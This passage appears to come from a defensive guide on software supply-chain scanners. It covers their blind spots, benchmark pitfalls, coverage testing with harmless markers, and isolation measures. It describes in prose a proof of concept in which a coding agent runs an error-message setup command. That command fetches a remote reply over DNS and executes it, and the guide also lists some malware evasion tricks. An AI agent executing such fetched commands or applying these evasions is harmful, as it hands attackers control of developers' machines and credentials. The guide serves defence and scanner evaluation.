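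The team should test the triage as well as the scanner. After every change to the grouping, filters or exceptions, they should run a set of known malicious packages through the whole process and count how many still reach a person. If a known attack no longer reaches anyone, they should reverse the change that caused the miss. They should also add recent attacks to the set and have a second person recheck a random sample of dismissed alarms each month.

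## Work out what a clean scan has not covered

A scan that finds nothing is evidence only about the files the scanner read. Suppose again that 1 package in 1,000 is malicious, and that a scanner catches 90% of the attacks in the files it reads. If it reads every file, about 1 in 10,000 of the packages it passes is malicious. If half of the attacks are in files it never opens, it catches only 45% of all attacks. About 1 in 1,800 of the packages it passes is then malicious, though the user sees the same clean result.

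Scanners leave more files unread than their users may expect. SocketAI, which uses a language model, read at most 20 files per package when Guo, Liu and colleagues (2026) tested it for *How Effective Are NPM Malicious Package Detectors?* Zhao, Wang and colleagues gave a model the full code of 250 malicious repositories before they built MalTotal, and 25.2% of the repositories were too long for its input. Bandit4Mal has to parse code before checking it, and *PyFEX* (Wang, Fan and colleagues, 2026) reports 95 parsing failures on its malicious packages and 39 on its benign ones. It is worth searching a scanner's log for files that it skipped, cut short or couldn't parse, and treating those files as unexamined.

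### What each kind of scanner can't see

The table assumes typical settings. "If given the file" means that a language model could judge the file, but only if the surrounding tool sends it to the model.

| Where the attack is | Pattern rules | Data-flow analysis | Language model | Sandboxed run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A dependency | Not seen | Not seen | Not seen | Seen if it runs |
| A compiled file | Known byte patterns only | Not seen | Not seen | Seen if it runs |
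| An unsupported language | Plain-text patterns only | Not seen | If given the file | Seen if it runs |
| A skipped folder or oversized file | Not seen | Not seen | Not seen | Seen if it runs |
| Install commands | With a rule for that file | Not seen | If given the file | Seen |
| Editor and agent settings | With a rule for that file | Not seen | If given the file | Not seen |
| Prose instructions to an agent | Known phrases and characters only | Not seen | If given the file | Not seen |
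| Content fetched at run time | The fetch only | The fetch only | The fetch only | Only what arrives during the test |
| Code that waits for a date, machine or call | Seen unless encoded | Seen unless encoded | Seen unless encoded | Not seen |

The other kinds of scanner have gaps too. Metadata checks don't open the files, and comparing a release with its source misses anything in both. A trained classifier depends on what its designers chose to measure. Combining a sandbox with a scanner that reads code fills many of these gaps, but every method has trouble with content that a program fetches when it runs.

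A clean scan often hasn't covered install commands. Guo, Liu and colleagues tested 11 npm scanners on 6,420 malicious package versions. In 21.2% of these, the attack consisted entirely of commands in `package.json`, which a scanner that reads only JavaScript can't find. EMPHunter, by contrast, reads only install scripts, so it doesn't cover the 1,184 malicious versions that don't have one.

A scanner built for npm may also ignore settings files for other languages. According to SafeDep's *Config Files That Run Code*, the Miasma worm started its program from seven kinds of settings file, including those of Composer and Bundler, which install PHP and Ruby packages.

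A scanner can also read the right file but have no rule for the kind of attack in it. GuardDog caught 89.9% of the malicious packages in the npm study, but only 7% of those that assemble code and immediately run it, and 27% of those that inject content into web pages. IntelGuard, the best scanner in the study, caught 98.5% of the packages that send data out but 62.5% of those that inject web content. Guo, Liu and colleagues say the scanners miss more web injections because they are all designed to analyse code meant for servers, whereas web injection happens in the browser.

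Wang and colleagues collected 417 malicious programs that attackers had written in Python and packed into executables. None of the existing Python scanners they tried could analyse them. Their tool, PyFEX, runs the compiled code and forces it down both branches of each condition, so malicious code can't stay hidden by running only under certain conditions. One piece of ransomware sleeps on any machine with less than 4 GB of memory, because test machines often have little memory.

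In Wang and colleagues' set of malicious PyPI packages, 59% either checked their surroundings in this way or hid the attack in a function that an ordinary test run wouldn't call. The npm study found evasion of any kind in only 19.7% of its packages. The two registries may attract different attackers, but the studies also counted differently. Wang and colleagues removed near-copies and included attacks that wait for a function call, which the npm study didn't list as evasion. Either figure is high enough that a sandbox run showing nothing suspicious isn't sufficient evidence that code is safe.

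### A repository with nothing malicious in it

In *Clone This Repo and I Own Your Machine*, Hall and Engelbrecht (2026) demonstrated an attack whose harmful part was never in the repository. They work for 0DIN, Mozilla's AI-security group, and built the repository themselves as a proof of concept.

The researchers asked Claude Code only to get a freshly downloaded project running. The agent read the setup notes and installed what the project needed, but the program failed to start and showed an error message containing a setup command. The agent ran that command, as many people would have. It started a script that looked up a setting on the internet and executed the reply as a command, which gave the researchers control of the machine with all the developer's permissions. The screen showed two routine messages about the setup.

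The harmful command in this attack was not in the repository, so scanners and reviewers could not have seen it there. But the script that executed whatever it received was in the repository, and a data-flow rule that follows text from the network to a command could flag it. Such a rule would also raise false alarms, because some legitimate installers work the same way. Hall and Engelbrecht overstate this when they write that no scanner would ever catch the attack. eWeek's *Clean GitHub Repo Attack Exposes AI Coding Agent Risk* (2026) makes the weaker claim that scanners and reviewers would have little to flag.

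A sandbox might not help either, because the attacker can change the reply at any time without editing the repository. The test machine could receive a harmless reply and the developer a different one a day later.

The demonstration shows that the attack is possible but doesn't measure how often it works. The researchers describe one agent and one project and don't say how many attempts they made, and 0DIN also markets AI-security products. Their advice is still sound. They want agents to show what a setup command will do, including the contents of any script it starts and anything that script fetches. Help Net Security's *Mozilla warns of indirect prompt injection risk in AI coding agents* (2026) reports that they also tell developers to treat setup instructions from unfamiliar repositories as untrusted code, whatever the agent recommends. In practice, this means following each setup command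 to its end. Examining the repository can't show that a command is safe if the command ends up fetching text from somebody else's server.

### Files too large for the model

A language model reads text as tokens, which are words or pieces of words, and it can take in only so many at once. Attackers can easily use up that limit. In an example from *CASHEWS* (Noirot Ferrand, Adei and colleagues, 2026), scrambling a program that prints "Hello World!" increased it from 6 tokens to 790. Miasma's list of 1.3 million numbers is far too long for many models, and scanners often skip such oversized files.

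CASHEWS shrinks JavaScript files before a model reads them, in four steps:

1. It decodes disguised text where it can, repeating the process if one layer hides another.
2. It separates the modules that developers have bundled into one file.
3. It removes code that doesn't affect any sensitive operation, such as a network request.
4. It shortens very long names and pieces of text.

If the result is still too large, the scanner receives only the three pieces with the most sensitive operations and data sources.

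The main test used 512 files, 166 of them malicious, each longer than 25,000 tokens (roughly 100 KB). Noirot Ferrand and colleagues counted every unscanned file as benign, because a registry as large as npm has too many to check by hand. They tried three models with a single question and with a three-stage review. The table compares the original files with the full CASHEWS process.

| Method and model | Malicious files missed | Benign files flagged | Files scanned |
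|---|---|---|---|
| One question, GPT-5 nano | 36.7% → 21.1% | 1.2% → 2.9% | 69.5% → 100% |
| One question, GPT-5.6 Luna | 34.9% → 19.3% | 0% → 0% | 69.7% → 100% |
| One question, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 34.3% → 15.7% | 0% → 0.9% | 69.7% → 100% |
| Three stages, GPT-5 nano | 30.1% → 16.3% | 1.2% → 2.6% | 69.1% → 98.8% |
| Three stages, GPT-5.6 Luna | 28.3% → 20.5% | 0.9% → 0.9% | 85.7% → 99.4% |
| Three stages, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 40.4% → 22.3% | 0% → 0.9% | 69.1% → 100% |

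The largest improvement came from DeepSeek with a single question. The number of malicious files it missed fell from 57 to 26 out of 166, but this added three false alarms among 346 benign files. If 1 large file in 1,000 were malicious, that would mean about 46 extra false alarms for each extra malicious file caught, although three false alarms are too few to estimate the rate precisely.

The last column counts a file as scanned even if the model saw only three pieces of it, and some bundles contain hundreds of modules. Some of the remaining misses happened because the malicious piece ranked fourth, so the model never saw it. A scanner that reports covering 100% of files may therefore have left a lot of code unread.

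CASHEWS also made some results worse when the researchers applied it to all 4,884 files in their collection, most of them much smaller. In the three-stage review, GPT-5.6 Luna missed 9.5% of the malicious files without CASHEWS and 13.1% with it. A team should therefore use it only on files that are too big to scan otherwise. It handles only JavaScript, and an attacker who knows the method could put harmful code in the part of a long text that it cuts out. Socket, which sells a scanner of this kind, employs the researchers and funded the work. The researchers warn that text in a repository can mislead a model that scans it.

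### Why benchmark recall overstates coverage

A scanner's recall on a benchmark can overstate how many different attacks it recognises, because many of the samples may be near-copies of one another. Suppose a benchmark contains 100 malicious packages, of which 80 are near-copies from one campaign and 20 are unrelated to those or to each other. A scanner that catches all the copies and half of the others has a recall of 90%, but it has recognised only 11 of 21 different attacks, or 52%.

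Real collections can be just as repetitive. Wang and colleagues started with 10,920 supposedly malicious PyPI packages from sources used in earlier studies. They removed 112 that turned out to be harmless, then kept one package from each group with the same structure, which left 2,961. GuardDog caught 77.0% of these, compared with 82.2% and 92.9% in the two earlier comparisons on Python packages, though those tests also differed in other ways.

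Copies are a bigger problem when some of them are in a scanner's training data. The scanner can then detect the rest because they match what it was trained on, which doesn't show how well it will handle a new campaign. Montaruli and colleagues found that attackers usually upload the near-identical packages of one campaign on the same day or within a few days. If researchers split a collection at random, such packages can easily end up in both the training and test data. *Measuring Duplication, Leakage, and Rendering Dependence in Malware-as-Image Benchmarks* (2026) gives an example from a benchmark that turns Android apps into images. Two apps have different hashes but identical images, and the published split puts one in the training data and the other in the test data.

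Copies can lower a detector's score as well as raise it. *Towards a Fair Comparison and Realistic Evaluation Framework of Android Malware Detectors* (2022) points out that when a detector misjudges a large group of copies, each one counts as an error. The study removed exact duplicates, which made up almost half of the malware, so they no longer distorted scores in either direction.

In *MaliciousSkillBench*, copies affected detection scores less than where the samples came from. The best trained detector scored 0.932 on a random split, where 1 is perfect, and 0.916 when the researchers kept related malicious skills on the same side of the split. On skills from collections it had never seen, it scored 0.665. It still caught 95.6% of the malicious skills there, but flagged 62.4% of the benign ones. Recall alone would not have revealed this failure, because a detector that flags most unfamiliar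 skills will catch most unfamiliar attacks.

A scanner that did well on old samples may also miss newer malware. In the npm study, one trained classifier caught 87% of the malicious packages from 2021 but only 39% of those from 2023. Another, Cerebro, caught 77% of those from 2022 but only 27% of those from 2024 and 2025. The malicious packages had become simpler, averaging 6.8 sensitive operations in 2023 compared with 12.5 in 2021, so they looked more like ordinary code. GuardDog's detection rate recovered after its maintainers updated its rules. *Research Methodologies for Cybersecurity in Enterprise Environments* (2026) therefore requires any claim about future performance to rest on a test whose samples are all later than the training data. A test of a scanner that looks up past reports needs the same separation, or the scanner may find a report on the package it is judging.

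Attackers also respond to scanners, usually in the way that takes the least effort. Guo, Liu and colleagues found encoded text in 19.3% of the malicious npm packages published up to 2020 but in only 2.3% of those from 2024 and 2025. Over the same period, the share using certain tricks with install scripts rose from 4.8% to 9.4%. The researchers conclude that attackers tend to drop a technique that scanners catch and move to a place that scanners don't inspect. Packages with four or more disguises were easier to catch than those with two or three. Which files a scanner reads therefore matters more to a buyer than whether it can defeat elaborate disguises.

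### Measure coverage with harmless markers

A team can find out what its scanner examines by planting harmless markers and counting how many the scanner reports. Antivirus users have long done something similar with EICAR, a harmless file that antivirus programs detect on purpose. No equivalent standard seems to exist for repositories, so the procedure below is a suggestion.

1. Copy a few ordinary repositories to an isolated machine, and don't publish the copies.
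2. Put a marker in each hiding place from the inventory. For a scanner with rules, the marker can be a unique piece of text, such as `COVERAGE-TEST-017`, together with a rule that flags it. For a language model, add a request to list every such text. For a sandbox, use a command that creates an empty file with that name.
3. Put some markers in plain view in ordinary source files. If the scanner misses those, the test itself is faulty.
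4. Run the scanner with its everyday settings, and count the markers it reports from each place.

Suppose the shop's developer puts one marker in each of eight places in five repositories, 40 in all.

| Place | Markers found, of 5 |
|---|---|
| Ordinary source file | 5 |
| Install script | 5 |
| Editor and agent settings | 5 |
| Agent instruction file | 4 |
| Large file | 4 |
| Test-data folder | 3 |
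| Compiled file | 0 |
| Dependency | 0 |
| Total | 26 of 40 |

The scanner found 26 of 40 markers, or 65%. The usual approximate 95% range for a share *p* of *n* independent trials is

p ± 1.96 × √(p × (1 − p) / n)

The 95% confidence interval here is 0.65 ± 1.96 × √(0.65 × 0.35 / 40), or about 50% to 80%. The true range is probably wider, because markers in the same kind of place tend to succeed or fail together.

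The rows are more useful than the total. The two zeros suggest that a clean result from this scanner is no evidence about compiled files or dependencies. The developer can confirm this in the scanner's documentation and then use another tool to cover them. The full scores are less conclusive, because a scanner that finds five out of five markers could still have a miss rate of up to about 45%. To show that it misses no more than 10% in a given place, the developer would need it to find every one of about 29 markers there.

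The 65% is not the chance of catching an attack, because a marker shows only that the scanner reads a place, not that it would detect malicious code there. Attackers also choose places deliberately, and one who knows that the scanner ignores compiled files will hide code in one, so the developer should keep the results private. The developer should also repeat the test whenever the scanner or its settings change.

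### Limit the harm from what gets through

Some attacks will pass every scan, so a team also needs to limit what those attacks can do. The most useful measure is isolation, which means an unfamiliar project, and any agent that works on it, should stay in a virtual machine like the one used for scanning, able to contact only the addresses the project needs. In the 0DIN demonstration, the harmful text arrived through DNS, the system that looks up internet names, so the restrictions have to cover those lookups too.

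eWeek also recommends requiring approval before an agent writes files or runs commands, and keeping a log of what it does. Approval is a weaker protection than isolation, because the command that an attacker wants approved may look like routine setup. The article cites a review of 78 studies in which attackers who adapted their text got past many published defences, and concludes that filters and warnings aren't enough by themselves.

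The machine should hold as few credentials as possible. The 0DIN attack gave the intruder every password and access token in the developer's environment, but testing a delivery calculator requires none of them. If a task needs a credential, that credential should expire soon and give access to only one thing, such as a test database. The team should keep a list of the credentials on each machine so that it knows which ones to replace after an incident.

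Turning off install scripts removes another common route of attack. Guo, Liu and colleagues found that 72.2% of the malicious npm packages used such scripts, and they suggest disabling them for untrusted packages. Some legitimate packages will then need a manual build step, and an attack like indexed-btree's will still get through.

Finally, the team should pin the versions of its dependencies. A lockfile records the exact version and hash of every package, including the dependencies of dependencies, so a new release can't enter the project until somebody chooses it. Except when a security fix is urgent, the team should wait a few days before upgrading, which gives others time to find an attack. A few days would have been more than enough to catch the Tensorlake release. A lockfile doesn't control what a program downloads for itself, so if a project fetches its setup commands from a server,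 the team should save a copy of those commands, review it, and run the setup from that copy with the network off.
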